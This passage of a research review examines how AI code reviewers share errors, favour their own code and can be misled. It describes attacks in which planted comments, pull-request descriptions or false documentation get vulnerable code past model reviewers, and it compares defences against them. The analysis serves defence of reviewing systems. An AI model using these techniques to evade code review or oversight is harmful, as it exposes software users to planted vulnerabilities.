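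*An Experimental Evaluation of the Assumption of Independence in Multi-Version Programming* (Knight and Leveson, 1986) tested whether such versions fail independently. Students at two universities wrote 27 versions of a program that decides from radar data whether to launch an anti-missile interceptor. They were told not to discuss the work with each other, and each version had to pass 200 random tests. Knight and Leveson then ran every version on a million more.

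Six of the programs never failed, and even the worst was right more than 99% of the time. But two or more programs failed together on 1,255 tests, about ten times the roughly 126 expected if they had failed independently. On two of the tests, eight programs failed at once.

One of the shared faults was in checking whether three points lie on a straight line, which they do if the angle between them is 0 or 180 degrees. More than one student forgot one of these cases. As a result, one version failed 231 times and another failed 37 times, always on inputs where the first version failed too.

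Knight and Leveson suggested that some parts of a problem are harder than others, so different people go wrong in the same places. They also suggested that compilers and ordinary testing remove the mistakes that only one person makes, and leave the subtle ones that many people share. They didn't blame the specification, which an earlier project had already tested. Supporters of N-version programming objected to the experiment, and in *A Reply to the Criticisms of the Knight & Leveson Experiment* the two researchers complained that some critics had misdescribed it. They had claimed only that the method may be less reliable than the theory predicts, not that it was useless.

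In *N-Version Programming with Coding Agents*, Ron, Baudry and Monperrus (2026) repeated the experiment with AI agents as the programmers. They used five agent products, models from several companies and three programming languages, and 48 versions passed the entry tests. Two or more versions failed together on 429 of a million inputs, compared with the 115 expected if the versions had failed independently. Many of these failures came from difficult or ambiguous parts of the specification.

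Voting still helped. A single version failed 387 times on average, and a group of three failed 131 times. But 11,844 of the 17,296 possible groups of three never failed, so the other 5,452 must have failed about 416 times each on average. A group can be wrong only where at least two versions fail, which happened on 429 inputs, so these groups failed on almost all of those inputs. Voting did very little for them, because two of the three members evidently shared the same fault.

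### Different companies, same wrong answers

*Correlated Errors in Large Language Models* (Kim, Garg et al., 2025) compares the answers of hundreds of models to multiple-choice questions. One data set covered 71 models and 14,042 questions. When two of these models were both wrong, they chose the same wrong answer 60% of the time on average, compared with 33% if they had picked among the wrong answers at random. In another set of 349 models, the figures were 42% and 13%.

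These percentages can't go into the formula as r. They measure how often two models make the same mistake when both are wrong, but the formula depends on how often both are wrong. When a verdict has only two options, two wrong reviewers always agree.

Goel, Strüber and colleagues (2025), in *Great Models Think Alike and this Undermines AI Oversight*, tested whether shared mistakes affect one model's judgement of another. They began by measuring how similar the models were on multiple-choice questions. Simple agreement is misleading, because two models that are each right 90% of the time will both be right on 81% of questions by chance. Their measure therefore removes the agreement that chance would produce:

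similarity = (observed agreement − chance agreement) / (1 − chance agreement)

It also counts two different wrong answers as a disagreement and accounts for the probability each model gave to each option. Nine models then judged whether written answers from 39 models were correct, without an answer key.

The judges gave higher marks to models that resembled them, with an average correlation of 0.84 between similarity and score, partly because the more accurate models also resembled the judges more. After the researchers allowed for accuracy, the correlation was still between 0.35 and 0.65 for every judge, possibly because a judge is less likely to mark an answer wrong if it would have made the same mistake. For example, a large Qwen model accepted 71% of the answers from a much smaller Qwen model and 67% of those from a Llama model, although the Llama model had done better on the multiple-choice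 questions (51% against 41%).

Goel and colleagues also compared 130 models with others of similar ability from different developers, and found that the more capable ones made more similar mistakes. Kim and colleagues found the same pattern. Goel and colleagues see this as a danger for AI oversight, since people may rely more on AI reviewers as models' mistakes become harder to find.

Two better models can still let less bad code through than two weaker ones, even if their errors are more correlated. If two reviewers each miss 20% of bad code and their errors have a correlation of 0.3, 8.8% gets past both. If two better reviewers each miss 10% and the correlation is 0.6, 6.4% gets past both. This improvement is much smaller than the individual miss rates suggest.

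Two studies from 2026 measured the correlation itself. Kohli (2026), in *Nine Judges, Two Effective Votes*, asked nine models from seven families whether one sentence follows from another. Their errors had an average correlation of 0.39. A standard formula converts this into the number of fully independent judges that would provide as much information, where k is the number of judges:

k / (1 + (k − 1)·r) = 9 / (1 + 8 × 0.39) ≈ 2.2

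All nine models on the panel were wrong on 51 of the 1,000 items. If their errors had been independent, less than one such item would be expected. The panel got 72.0% right, and its best single member got 71.8%. Some of the answers counted as errors may be legitimate readings of an ambiguous sentence, since Kohli marked an answer wrong whenever it differed from the majority of 100 people.

*Agreement Overstates Evidence* (2026) found a lower average correlation, 0.21, among ten judges comparing pairs of answers. At that level, the ten judges provided about as much evidence as 3.5 independent ones.

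### Two reviewers of the same code

Thornton's results suggest that the same thing happens when models look for faults in code, which none of those tasks involved. Four of the five commercial models missed the login check that leaked secrets through its timing, even without any misleading comments. If the models had made errors independently at their overall rates, the chance of four or more missing the same fault anywhere in the 100 programs would have been about 1%.

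*When Does a Second Model Help?* (Song, 2026) compared pairs of reviewers on 150 errors planted in 30 pieces of work by Claude Opus 4.6. Ten of the pieces were code, and the rest were tutorials and presentation scripts. In one run, a fresh session of Claude found 56 of the errors and GPT-5.4 found 64. Together they found 85 and missed 65. If their misses had been independent, they would have missed about 54 of the same errors. The correlation between their misses was roughly 0.31.

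| Study | Reviewers | Task | Error correlation | Both miss, if each misses 10% |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| *Agreement Overstates Evidence* | Ten judges | Comparing two answers | 0.21 | 2.9% |
| Song | Claude Opus 4.6 and GPT-5.4 | Finding planted errors in code and documents | 0.31 (our calculation) | 3.8% |
| Kohli | Nine models from seven families | Judging whether one sentence follows from another | 0.39 | 4.5% |

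If these correlations hold for hostile code, a second reviewer would catch about 55% to 71% of what the first one missed. That is well worth having, though well below the 90% it would catch if the two reviewers' errors were independent.

Two Claude reviews together found only 64 of Song's planted errors, and replacing one with a GPT-5.4 review helped a good deal. But GPT-5.4 may just have been the better reviewer, since two GPT-5.4 reviews did almost as well as the mixed pair and the difference wasn't statistically significant. On code alone, Claude had the best score for a single review, even though it was reviewing its own work. The score combined the share of planted errors found with the share of reports that matched a planted error.

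Song's evidence has other weaknesses. Software matched the reviewers' reports to the planted errors, and nobody checked its accuracy by hand. The records of the Claude reviews contain no raw output, so Song treats them as unverified.

A fair test has to run the same model again as well as a different one, because two runs of one model also find different things. *We Fixed the Scorer First* (2026) compares two model families on a single code change but warns against attributing the result to model family, because each family ran only once and only one of the reviewers could execute code.

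### Where shared errors come from

Developers train their models on much of the same public text and code, using similar methods. Kim and colleagues found that two models from the same company agreed on wrong answers 2 to 7 percentage points more often than other pairs. But agreement was also high between models from different companies, so choosing a different supplier removes only a small part of the problem. One Google model and one from the company Writer gave the same answer on 99.87% of the questions that both got wrong, although the researchers knew of no public connection between them. *Agreement Overstates Evidence* found that changing the model family, the prompt style or the training seed (the starting point for randomness in training) didn't eliminate shared errors.

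*The Specification as Quality Gate* (2026) applies this argument to code, where the model that writes a program and the model that reviews it may share a misunderstanding. Automated tests may not help if a model wrote them too. The paper cites research in which AI-written tests concentrated on the kinds of mistakes language models make and neglected others that are common among human programmers.

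Shared training also lets an attacker practise on the wrong model. Suppose the attacker can't reach a platform's reviewer, but finds code that slips past another model that anyone can use. If each model misses 10% of bad code and their errors have a correlation of 0.3, the platform's reviewer will miss that code 37% of the time:

0.10 + 0.3 × 0.90 = 0.37

Planted text can make both reviewers misjudge code that they would otherwise have judged correctly. *ALIBI* attributes its results to a tendency, common across detectors, to give too much weight to plausible comments they can't verify. Its attack worked on models from two families, Alibaba's Qwen and OpenAI's GPT. However, the attacker tailored its comments to each detector, so the experiment doesn't show that one comment would fool all four detectors.

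Melo and colleagues gave the same descriptions to eight agents, and some kinds of description that usually fooled the weaker agents seldom fooled the three strongest. So susceptibility to a given text is only partly shared. But correlations measured on unintentional mistakes may understate how often models fail together on hostile code, since an attacker can look for text that fools several models.

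The remaining cause is that both models read the same false information, and it has little to do with how similar the models are. Suppose someone falsely claims in a project's documentation that a certain function removes dangerous input. A coding agent reads the claim and leaves out a check that it would otherwise have written. The reviewer notices that the check is missing, reads the same documentation and accepts the omission. This could happen even if the two models came from different companies and had nothing in common except that page. The attacker may not need to submit any code, because the coding agent writes the vulnerability.

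*ALIBI* notes that a project contributor could manipulate a coding agent with malicious instructions. But its experiments used an agent that wrote vulnerable code on purpose, so they don't measure how often the same text would mislead both an honest agent and its reviewer. The nearest figures are second-hand, from a September 2026 experiment that *We Fixed the Scorer First* cites. When different models voted after reading the same evidence, they approved 62.9% of risky proposals, compared with 22.9% when they had independent sources of evidence.

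If that result holds for code, changing what the reviewer reads may matter more than changing the reviewer. In the documentation example, a second model would help much more if it read the function itself or tested it with dangerous input than if it only read the same page.

### One model in several roles

Some review systems give one model several roles. In VulTrial, one of *ALIBI*'s four detectors, several agents debate whether the code is vulnerable, and a review board gives the verdict. All of these roles use GPT-4o.

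A role is a set of instructions that can direct the model's attention to something a general review would miss. An agent told to argue that the code is dangerous may well find evidence that an agent told to defend it would overlook. But every role depends on the same training. If GPT-4o hasn't learned that a particular function can return an empty value, telling it to act as a prosecutor won't supply that fact. A false comment that misleads the defender will probably mislead the board as well.

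Having one model read the same code several times and taking a majority vote can correct chance errors, but it also makes the model's usual answer more likely to win, even when that answer is wrong. If a model notices a fault in 70% of its readings, a majority of three independent readings will catch it 78% of the time. If the model notices the fault in only 20% of its readings, a majority of three will catch it only 10% of the time.

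Debate can reduce independence further, because each participant reads what the others have said. Song describes an earlier pilot in which one model played a worker, a verifier and a director. The later stages could see the earlier conclusions and merely confirmed them. In the main experiment, a second review in the same conversation scored worse than the first.

The attack in *ALIBI* succeeded against VulTrial, as it did against the other detectors, so VulTrial's debate didn't prevent it. But the study didn't test GPT-4o alone on the same code, so we can't tell whether the debate made the attack harder or easier.

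### A stronger model from the same family

Two reviewers together can't miss more bad code than the better one misses alone. If a weak model misses 20% of bad code and a stronger model from the same company misses 5%, at most 5% gets past both, however similar their errors are. If the second reviewer were instead an unrelated model that misses 30%, about 6% would get past both, even if the two models' errors were independent. So a better model from the same company can be a better second reviewer than a worse one from elsewhere.

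Gong and colleagues have some evidence that a stronger model from the same developer can help. They tried the 33 attacks that had succeeded against Anthropic's Claude Sonnet 5 on the more capable Claude Fable 5.1, with the same review instructions. Fable 5.1 rejected 26 in the first round and still withheld approval from 18 after five rounds.

Fable 5.1's greater ability may not explain all 18 of its catches. The researchers chose these cases because Sonnet 5 had failed on them, and it probably failed on some by chance. They didn't run Sonnet 5 again with the same instructions to find out how many. When Alexopoulos and colleagues had Claude Code review pull requests it had already approved, it rejected 24% of them. At a similar rate, Sonnet 5 would catch about 8 of the 33 on a second run. With stricter instructions, Sonnet 5 caught more than 18, so the original misses weren't all beyond its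 ability.

The same study's main result might suggest the opposite effect, that a model is worse at catching attacks written by a copy of itself. Sonnet 5 played the attacker throughout, and it got vulnerable code past a Sonnet 5 reviewer in 33 of 159 cases and past GPT-5.5 in 25.

The figures don't establish this. The difference is eight cases, and the 95% confidence intervals overlap widely (15% to 28% for Sonnet 5 and 11% to 22% for GPT-5.5). The reviewers also ran in different tools, Claude Code and Codex, and GPT-5.5 may be better at reviewing code regardless of who wrote it. A proper test would include GPT-5.5 as the attacker, to see whether the gap reversed. In the team's preliminary trials, GPT-5.5 usually refused to act as the attacker.

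## Does a model judge its own code more leniently?

Coding agents often write a change and then tell the user whether it is correct. In some experiments, models judge their own code more leniently, mostly when they review it in the same conversation where they wrote it. Discussions often conflate three effects that need different tests.

Self-preference is a model's tendency to rate its own output above equally good output from others, even when the authors aren't identified. A model may also judge work more leniently because a label names the model as the author. It may also fail to correct an error in its own messages that it would correct in a user's message.

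| Effect | What researchers compare | What they have to rule out |
|---|---|---|
| Self-preference | A model's votes for its own unlabelled answers and for other answers | Its own answers are better, or it can't tell good answers from bad |
| Authorship labels | Ratings of the same work under different labels | The works differ in quality |
| Uncorrected errors | Corrections of the same error in the model's message and in the user's | The model doesn't know the right answer |

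### Recognizing and preferring its own text

Panickssery, Bowman and Feng (2024), in *LLM Evaluators Recognize and Favor Their Own Generations*, tested GPT-3.5, GPT-4 and Llama 2 on summaries of news articles, not on code. They showed a model two unlabelled summaries, one of them its own, and asked which was better or which it had written. GPT-4 identified its own summaries with 73.5% accuracy, compared with 50% for guessing.

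The order of the summaries also affected the answers. When the researchers swapped the two texts, GPT-4 reversed its choice in 25% of cases and Llama 2 in 89%. They therefore asked every question in both orders and averaged the results.

Comparing two models' votes on each other's summaries can reveal self-preference without human ratings. Suppose GPT-4 gives 60% of its vote to its own summaries over GPT-3.5's, and GPT-3.5 gives 60% to its own over GPT-4's. The two shares add up to more than 100%, so at least one model must overrate its own summaries. The total exceeded 100% for every pair of models.

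After training on examples from 500 articles, GPT-3.5 and Llama 2 recognized their own summaries more than 90% of the time. Among the differently trained versions, those that were better at recognizing their own summaries also tended to prefer them more strongly. The researchers suspected that recognition causes the preference but acknowledged that a correlation doesn't prove it.

They also tried false labels. On one of the two sets of articles, GPT-3.5 and GPT-4 preferred whichever summary was labeled as their own, even when the label was false. The labels made no clear difference on the other set, or to Llama 2.

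### When its own program really is better

A model may prefer its own code because that code is better, just as a good programmer may prefer their own code to a beginner's. It is hard to tell whether such a preference is justified when models judge summaries, because a summary has no single correct answer. *Do LLM Evaluators Prefer Themselves for a Reason?* (Chen, Wei and colleagues, 2025) instead used maths problems, factual questions and short Python tasks, with automated tests to check whether each Python program worked.

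Eleven models compared their own answers with those of seven other models. The researchers then looked at the cases where exactly one of the two answers was correct. They counted a model's preference for its own answer as deserved if that answer was correct and undeserved if it wasn't.

The models' preference for their own answers was mostly justified. On the programming and factual tasks, two of the largest models were right 81% to 89% of the time when they chose their own answers. Models that wrote better programs also judged programs better (correlation 0.90). But large models still chose their own program in roughly 50% to 75% of cases where it was wrong and the other program was right.

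An invented example shows how both results can hold. Suppose a model's program is the correct one in 80 of 100 comparisons. The model chooses its own program in 76 of those 80, and in 12 of the 20 where its own is wrong. It is then right in 76 of the 88 comparisons where it chooses its own program (86%), but it misses 12 of its 20 faulty programs (60%). The 60% matters more for code review, because only those 20 programs have a fault to catch.

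Even the undeserved votes may not be favouritism. A model that writes a faulty program may have misunderstood the task, and would then accept another model's faulty program too. Roytburg, Bozoukov and colleagues (2026), in *Are LLM Evaluators Really Narcissists?*, tested this by replacing the judge's wrong answer with a wrong answer from a different model:

favouritism = vote for own wrong answer − vote for another model's wrong answer

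Across all their tests, this control removed about 90% of the apparent self-preference. The results for the five largest models on the Python tasks show how much remained.

| Model | Average vote for own wrong program | Favouritism |
|---|---|---|
| Gemma 2 27B | 41.0% | 8.4 points |
| Qwen 2.5 32B | 15.3% | 0.5 points |
| Llama 3.1 70B | 37.8% | 6.5 points |
| Llama 3.3 70B | 38.7% | 9.0 points |
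| Qwen 2.5 72B | 25.8% | 10.3 points |

Seven of the 11 models tested on these tasks still preferred their own wrong programs by a statistically significant margin, between 1 and 10 points. So self-preference exists for code, but it is much smaller than it appears from the raw votes.

Roytburg and colleagues also repeated the news-summary experiment with this control. GPT-3.5 and GPT-4 were 18 to 23 points less likely to vote for their own inferior summaries than for other models' inferior summaries. This makes it less likely that the models voted for their own inferior summaries because they recognized them. It doesn't overturn the original finding, because the repeat covered only cases where the judge's own summary was worse, and GPT-5 decided which those were.

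The two teams disagree about whether having a model reason before it votes helps. Chen and colleagues found that it reduced undeserved self-preference. The other team, which used a stricter control, found that the benefit was inconsistent and that Qwen models seemed to favour themselves more.

These programming results come from 2024 models choosing between two programs. An extension reviewer usually has only one program and must accept or reject it, so a 10-point preference doesn't mean a 10-point higher approval rate.

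### The conversation matters more than the label

In *Self-Attribution Bias*, Khullar, Hopkins and colleagues (2026) tested how models judge single pieces of code. They had models write patches for reported problems in real software projects and then rate whether each patch was correct. The projects' own tests showed which patches worked.

A model rated its own patch in the reply that contained it, in its next reply, or in a new conversation where the user's message contained the patch. The patch was the same each time, so its quality couldn't explain a change in the rating.

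The researchers used AUROC to measure how well the ratings separated working patches from failing ones. AUROC is the chance that a randomly chosen working patch gets a higher rating than a randomly chosen failing one.

| Where the model rated its own patch | AUROC | Pairs in the wrong order |
|---|---|---|
| New conversation | 0.99 | 1% |
| Next reply | 0.92 | 8% |
| Same reply | 0.89 | 11% |

The ratings rose mostly for patches that didn't work. The size of the effect varied between models and tasks. These figures appear to come from a comparison involving GPT-5 and Claude Sonnet 4.

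When the researchers put another model's patch in the same position in the conversation, the score stayed at 0.99, so the wording of the request can't explain the difference. A company could also test its reviewer on other models' code, get an excellent result and miss the problem.

In a second coding experiment, the researchers planted comments that seemed to come from a project's maintainers and encouraged unsafe code, such as database queries open to SQL injection. They kept only the cases where the model had written the unsafe code, then asked it whether to approve the patch. In one version of the test, a model was five times as likely to approve the patch when it appeared as the model's own earlier work.

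An attacker could therefore benefit twice from one planted comment, when the agent writes the vulnerability and when the same agent reviews it. The comment might explain some of the leniency, since the model had read it before writing the patch. But the comment alone wouldn't explain why the bias was again strongest when models judged their own patches.

Telling the model who wrote an insecure patch had little effect. Its average rating usually stayed within half a point on a 10-point scale, whether the researchers attributed the patch to that model, to another model, or to no one. Longer reasoning didn't consistently reduce the bias either.

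Khullar and colleagues think deliberate deception is an unlikely explanation for a model approving its own bad code. A model that was protecting its own work would have reason to respond to the label too, and these models hardly did. The researchers also cite earlier work that traced self-preference to models giving higher marks to text that is more predictable to them, as their own text usually is. A model can do this without intending to favor its own work or even recognizing it.

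### Errors already in the conversation

*Large Language Models Cannot Self-Correct Reasoning Yet* (Huang, Chen and colleagues, 2023) found that asking a model to check its previous answer without giving it new information could make answers worse. On 200 school maths problems, GPT-4's accuracy fell from 95.5% to 91.5% after one round of checking and to 89.0% after two. GPT-3.5's accuracy on common-sense questions fell from 75.8% to 38.1% after one round.

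Earlier studies had reported improvements because the researchers used the correct answers to decide when the model should stop revising. GPT-4's score on the maths problems rose to 97.5% with that help, but the models couldn't reliably identify their wrong answers by themselves.

None of these tasks involved code, and leniency didn't cause the decline. A lenient checker would have left the answers alone, but on the maths problems GPT-3.5 changed more right answers to wrong ones than the reverse.

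Tsui (2025), in *Self-Correction Bench*, separated errors that a model can't correct from errors that it could correct but doesn't. Tsui put the same mistake either in the user's message or at the start of the model's reply, and measured how often the model still reached the right answer:

blind spot = 1 − (success after an error in its own reply / success after the same error in the user's message)

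The average blind spot across 14 openly available models without special training in reasoning was 64.5%. For example, a model that recovered from 80% of the errors in the user's messages but only 28% of the same errors in its own replies would have a blind spot of about that size. The problems tested were maths and logic, not code.

Tsui inserted these errors rather than using ones the models had made, so the experiment measures the effect of where an error appears, not of who made it. When Tsui instead presented models' own errors as someone else's, the models caught only 4.3% to 10.8% of them. Moving an error out of the conversation helps only if the model can recognize it, and these models usually couldn't.

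Tsui traces the blind spot to the conversations used to train ordinary models, which almost never show a speaker making a mistake and correcting it. Training a small Llama model on 5,306 examples of reasoning, which often included corrections, reduced its blind spot by 76%. Just adding the word "Wait" after the error reduced the average blind spot by 89.3%, so the models were often able to correct themselves but didn't do so without a cue.

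Models trained to reason had little or no blind spot in these tests, so the 64.5% average is probably too high for current coding agents, which often reason before they answer. But reasoning models still showed the bias that Khullar and colleagues found in code ratings.

### Models reviewing their own programs

*Cross-Model LLM Code Review* (Xiang, Zhang et al., 2026) tested Claude Opus 4.7 and GPT-5.5 as reviewers of their own and each other's programs. Each model wrote solutions to 116 programming-contest problems published after its training data ended. A reviewer then received the problem and the draft without being told which model had written it. The reviewer couldn't run code, and returned either the same program or a corrected one.

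| Writer | Reviewer | Wrong drafts fixed | Correct drafts broken | Correct after review |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude | Claude | 3 of 10 | 3 of 106 | 91.4% |
| Claude | GPT-5.5 | 3 of 10 | 13 of 106 | 82.8% |
| GPT-5.5 | GPT-5.5 | 21 of 33 | 6 of 83 | 84.5% |
| GPT-5.5 | Claude | 26 of 33 | 5 of 83 | 89.7% |

GPT-5.5 fixed nearly two thirds of its own wrong programs, so it often caught its own mistakes. Claude fixed slightly more of GPT-5.5's wrong programs, but it was also the better programmer on these problems. Claude's review of its own work brought no overall improvement, and having GPT-5.5 review that work instead made the results worse. Differences in the reviewers' ability explain these results at least as well as leniency towards their own code.

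Some of the fixes may not have come from reviewing, because the reviewer could write a new program. Xiang and colleagues didn't test how often a model would succeed if it tried the problem again without seeing the draft. The experiment also measured the final program rather than a verdict, so it doesn't show how often a model would have approved its own faulty code.

Self-review can also be too harsh. In *Reviewer Capability Governs Rejection Targeting, Not Repair Skill* (2026), a model reviewing its own answers caught a larger share of the errors than any other reviewer tested, but also rejected 35% of the correct answers. It made 6.6 rejections for every useful repair, compared with 2.3 for a reviewer from another model family. Only the other family's reviews significantly improved the final answers.

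The false rejections did little damage because the model revising the work returned the same correct answer after 15 of the 18. An extension scanner that blocked a file after every rejection wouldn't have that protection.

The evidence that a fresh session finds more faults is weaker than it first appeared. Song reported an advantage in *Cross-Context Review* (2026) but later found that one set of same-session results might not be raw model output. Without that set, Song's combined score was 28.6% for fresh-session review and 27.1% for same-session review, a difference that wasn't statistically significant. The fresh reviewer also didn't see the user's original request, so the comparison changed two things at once.

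### What a fresh session or a different model changes

A user can easily keep the code out of the model's own turns by giving the files to a new session. In the patch experiment, that was enough to restore the accuracy of the model's ratings.

Hiding the author's name does much less. A model may recognize its own style anyway, and the labels hardly affected ratings of insecure patches.

Using a different model as the reviewer avoids self-review, but that model may be worse at reviewing, as GPT-5.5 was for Claude's programs. It may also share many of the first model's errors, for the reasons given in the previous section.

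When a user asks about an extension, a stranger has usually written the code, so the assistant isn't judging its own work unless it helped write or adapt the extension earlier in the conversation. The situation may be similar if the assistant recommended the extension, although none of these experiments tested that. In either case, a user who wants a second opinion would do better to ask in a new session.

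The stranger may also have written the extension with the same model that reviews it. An attacker who knows which model a platform uses could do this on purpose. The Python results suggest that any advantage from self-preference would be small, and the one comparison of Claude and GPT-5.5 as reviewers of Claude's attacks was inconclusive.

None of these changes gives the reviewer new evidence about the code, so a false claim in the documentation can mislead a new session or a different model too. The reviewer needs evidence that doesn't depend on the author's account, such as test results or static analysis.

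## Which defences help, and what do they cost?

Developers can defend an AI reviewer by warning it in its instructions, changing what it reads, giving it evidence that the code's author didn't write, or limiting the harm that a mistake can do. Warnings are the easiest of these to add and the least effective.

### Warnings in the prompt

A warning can help against text that an attacker wrote in advance. Thornton told the models to treat all comments as untrusted and to judge only the working code. With false comments and no warning, the five commercial models missed 14 faults that they found in uncommented code. With the warning, they missed four of these faults. When they were instead told to trace data through the program step by step, they missed ten.

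The attacker in *ALIBI* can rewrite a comment after each refusal, and a warning did much less there. The researchers tested four defences:

- a plain warning to distrust comments
- an instruction to reach a verdict from the code first, then change it only on finding a genuine mistake
- a separate analysis of the code without its comments, which the detector received before it read the commented version
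- a filter, in which another model removed comments that nobody could check against the visible code

| Defence | OpenVul | VulnLLM-R | Vul-RAG | VulTrial |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 97.4% | 91.2% | 95.5% | 100% |
| Warning | 93.9% | 93.8% | 42.3% | 99.0% |
| Code first, in the same prompt | 91.3% | 92.9% | 48.6% | 100% |
| Separate code-only analysis | 49.6% | 0% | 49.5% | 96.2% |
| Comment filter (finished comments only) | 2.5% | 2.8% | 0.4% | 0.6% |

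The percentages are attack success rates, so lower is better. The warning left them above 90% on three of the four detectors. The slight rise for VulnLLM-R amounts to three programs out of 113 and could be chance.

This is partly because the attacker can adapt. When the researchers replayed the first comments from the undefended test, the warning cut the attack's success rate against OpenVul from 81.7% to 67.0%. Five rounds of rewriting the comments raised it to 93.9%. The detectors' output often described the comment as untrusted, and even cited the warning, but still relied on the comment's claim. OpenVul and VulTrial repeated the claim as fact, while Vul-RAG searched the code for evidence to support it.

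The separate analysis stopped every attack on VulnLLM-R and about half of those on OpenVul. It hardly helped VulTrial, whose agents debate earlier findings and could still overturn the code-only result because of the comment. A separate analysis therefore protects the verdict only if later steps can't overturn it because of something the code's author wrote.

That rule also stops comments written in good faith from overriding the result, including those that correctly explain why dangerous-looking code is safe. *ALIBI* tested no harmless programs, so we don't know how many false alarms VulnLLM-R would have raised with this defence.

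### Filtering out claims that nobody can check

The filter scored far better than the other defences, but on an easier test. Against the other defences, the attacker could try ten kinds of comment and rewrite each one up to five times. For the filter, the researchers counted how many finished comments from earlier attacks got past it, so the attacker never saw the filter or adapted to it.

The percentages also appear to count comments, not programs. If each of ten comments on a program had an independent 2.8% chance of getting past the filter, at least one would do so for about a quarter of programs:

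1 − 0.972¹⁰ ≈ 0.25

The real figure is probably lower, since a filter that catches one comment on a program will tend to catch similar ones. But it could easily be above 3%.

The comments also suited the filter unusually well, because the researchers had told the attacker to make only claims that a reader of the file couldn't check, which are the claims the filter removes. An attacker facing a filter would have reason to make claims that look checkable, but this would constrain the attacker, because the reviewer could then check them. However, the filter is itself a language model reading hostile text, and *ALIBI* cites earlier research in which defences of this kind became much weaker once attackers optimized against them.

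Filtering requires an extra model call and discards some useful information. Honest programmers often write a comment because the reason for the code is in another file. The filter would remove many of these comments, and *ALIBI* doesn't report how many.

### Removing every comment

Cloudflare recommends removing all comments before the review and calls this "trivial but highly effective". It doesn't report testing this, and its own results give the recommendation little support. On average, its seven models flagged more malicious scripts with 1,000 reassuring comments than with none, so removing the comments would have lowered detection. Two of the cheaper models were exceptions, including the one that 20 comments had misled badly.

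Thornton did test removal and advises against it, because it seemed to hurt weaker models. The experiment compared four defences on four commercial models.

| Model | No defence | Comments removed | Reviewed with and without comments | Suspicious comments flagged | Static-analysis hints |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.6 | 94.0% | 96.9% | 97.2% | 96.9% | 97.2% |
| GPT-5.2 | 91.9% | 95.9% | 97.2% | 96.9% | 97.2% |
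| DeepSeek Chat | 93.0% | 89.0% | 94.5% | 92.8% | 96.6% |
| Perplexity Sonar Pro | 92.0% | 91.0% | 95.5% | 93.8% | 96.6% |

Removal appears to have helped Opus and GPT-5.2 and hurt the other two, but this comparison may be unreliable because the first column probably covers a different mix of programs from the rest. All the defence percentages fit a total of 290 reviews per model, which would match two versions of all 100 programs plus three more versions of the 30 easier ones. In that case, the easier programs would make up about half of the reviews instead of 30%.

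The results for flagging suspicious comments suggest the same conclusion. This defence had an overall detection rate of 95.1%, compared with 92.5% for no defence, yet it recovered none of the faults that the models had missed without a defence. If both rates covered the same programs, the defence would have to recover some of those faults to reach the higher rate.

Comparing the defences with each other is therefore safer. Removing comments did no better than keeping and flagging them for Opus, and did worse for the other three models, by 1.0 to 3.8 points. DeepSeek had the largest drop, to 89.0%, but it scored the same on uncommented code in the main experiment, where the difference between commented and uncommented code wasn't statistically significant. Thornton therefore has some evidence that removing comments lowers detection in "weaker models", but it is weak and comes mostly from DeepSeek.

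The two recommendations also assume different attackers. Thornton's fixed comments did little net harm, so removing them could help only a little. If an attacker has refined a comment over dozens of tries, it may do a great deal of harm, and removing comments is then worth losing some honest context.

Reviewing the code both with and without comments mostly avoids having to choose between keeping and removing them. Thornton's version reports any fault that either review finds, so a false comment can hide a fault only if the model also misses it in the code without comments. It scored 96.1% overall and caught 20 of 57 earlier misses, at twice the price. It probably also raises more false alarms, since either review can raise one, but Thornton didn't measure them.

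Removing comments leaves an attacker other places to write. In the npm package that Koi found, the planted sentence was in a variable, so removing comments would have left it in place. Removal also doesn't help with very large scripts, most of which Cloudflare's models missed even without added comments. For those, Cloudflare suggests prioritising working code when a script has to be cut to fit, and separating the author's code from standard libraries. It also suggests asking about one kind of abuse at a time. It reports no tests of these measures as defences either.

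A scanner that removes comments should first check them for messages addressed to an AI reviewer, because such messages are good evidence that something is wrong.

### Hiding the description and the replies

A pull request's title and description are easier to do without than comments, because they aren't part of the program. Alexopoulos and colleagues report that withholding this text from the reviewer restored detection in every case where their adaptive attack had worked. But the attacker had developed those descriptions against a reviewer that could read them, so the test doesn't measure how well an attack would work if the same effort went into the code.

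In Gong and colleagues' tests against Claude Sonnet 5, an attacker that could rewrite the description and answer the reviewer as well as change the code succeeded about twice as often as one that could only change the code. Hiding the author's text from the reviewer might therefore prevent about half of such an attacker's successes.

In one case, a reviewer that saw only the code noticed that a harmful key could still get through. When the attacker could also write to the reviewer, the attacker fixed one route and told the reviewer that the program's existing structure protected the other. The reviewer accepted this without working out which key each check examined.

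Without a description, however, the reviewer doesn't know what the change is for, so it can't report that a supposed spelling correction also alters the login code. A team could have the model review the code alone first, then compare the description with the change in a second step that can add objections but not withdraw any. None of these studies tested that arrangement.

### Telling the author less

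Attackers learn from a reviewer's explanations, so Gong and colleagues recommend withholding the location and explanation of security problems. In their experiment, this cut the attacker's success rate by about two fifths.

Honest authors learn from explanations too. Gong and colleagues cite an experiment in which coding agents revised 100 patches that a reviewer had correctly rejected. The agents solved the problem in 8% of cases when they saw only the verdict, and in 21% when they also saw an explanation. Withholding explanations would therefore slow ordinary repairs, perhaps more than it slows attackers.

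Withholding feedback also works only if the attacker can't get the explanations elsewhere. Anyone can run Claude Code on a private copy of a project and read everything the model says about the change. Withholding makes more sense for a store with its own scanner, because outsiders can't run a copy. The store could send the full explanation to a staff member, who decides what to tell the developer.

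### Hints from static analysis

The best result in Thornton's comparison came from static analysis. A conventional tool first scanned the program, and the model then received instructions to verify each finding, listed with its line number. Detection was 96.9% overall, and the models found 27 of the 57 faults they had previously missed (47%). The method needs no extra model calls, and conventional scans take little compute.

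The test strongly favoured this defence, though, because Thornton had confirmed in advance that static tools could detect every fault in the collection. The keyword scoring also helped. A hint about SQL injection supplies the keyword, so a model that repeated the hint and dismissed it as a false alarm could have received credit.

The count of 57 misses is also unclear. Thornton describes them as misses in the version with simple false comments, but the main results for these four models include only about 27 such misses. The 57 probably include misses in other versions of the same programs.

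Liu and Gao (2026), in *Trusting the Tool*, found much less benefit in real code. They used C and C++ functions with known vulnerabilities and the developers' fixed versions of those functions. A static analyser listed each function's risky operations, the checks that protected them and the protections that seemed to be missing. Adding this information to the prompt raised accuracy by only 2 percentage points, and the true effect could be zero.

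The two results are compatible because Thornton's tools pointed to the actual fault, while Liu and Gao's analyser mostly described what a careful reader could already see. Static analysis helps a reviewer most when it finds something the reviewer would miss, and how often that happens depends on the tool and the code.

### When the tool's report is wrong

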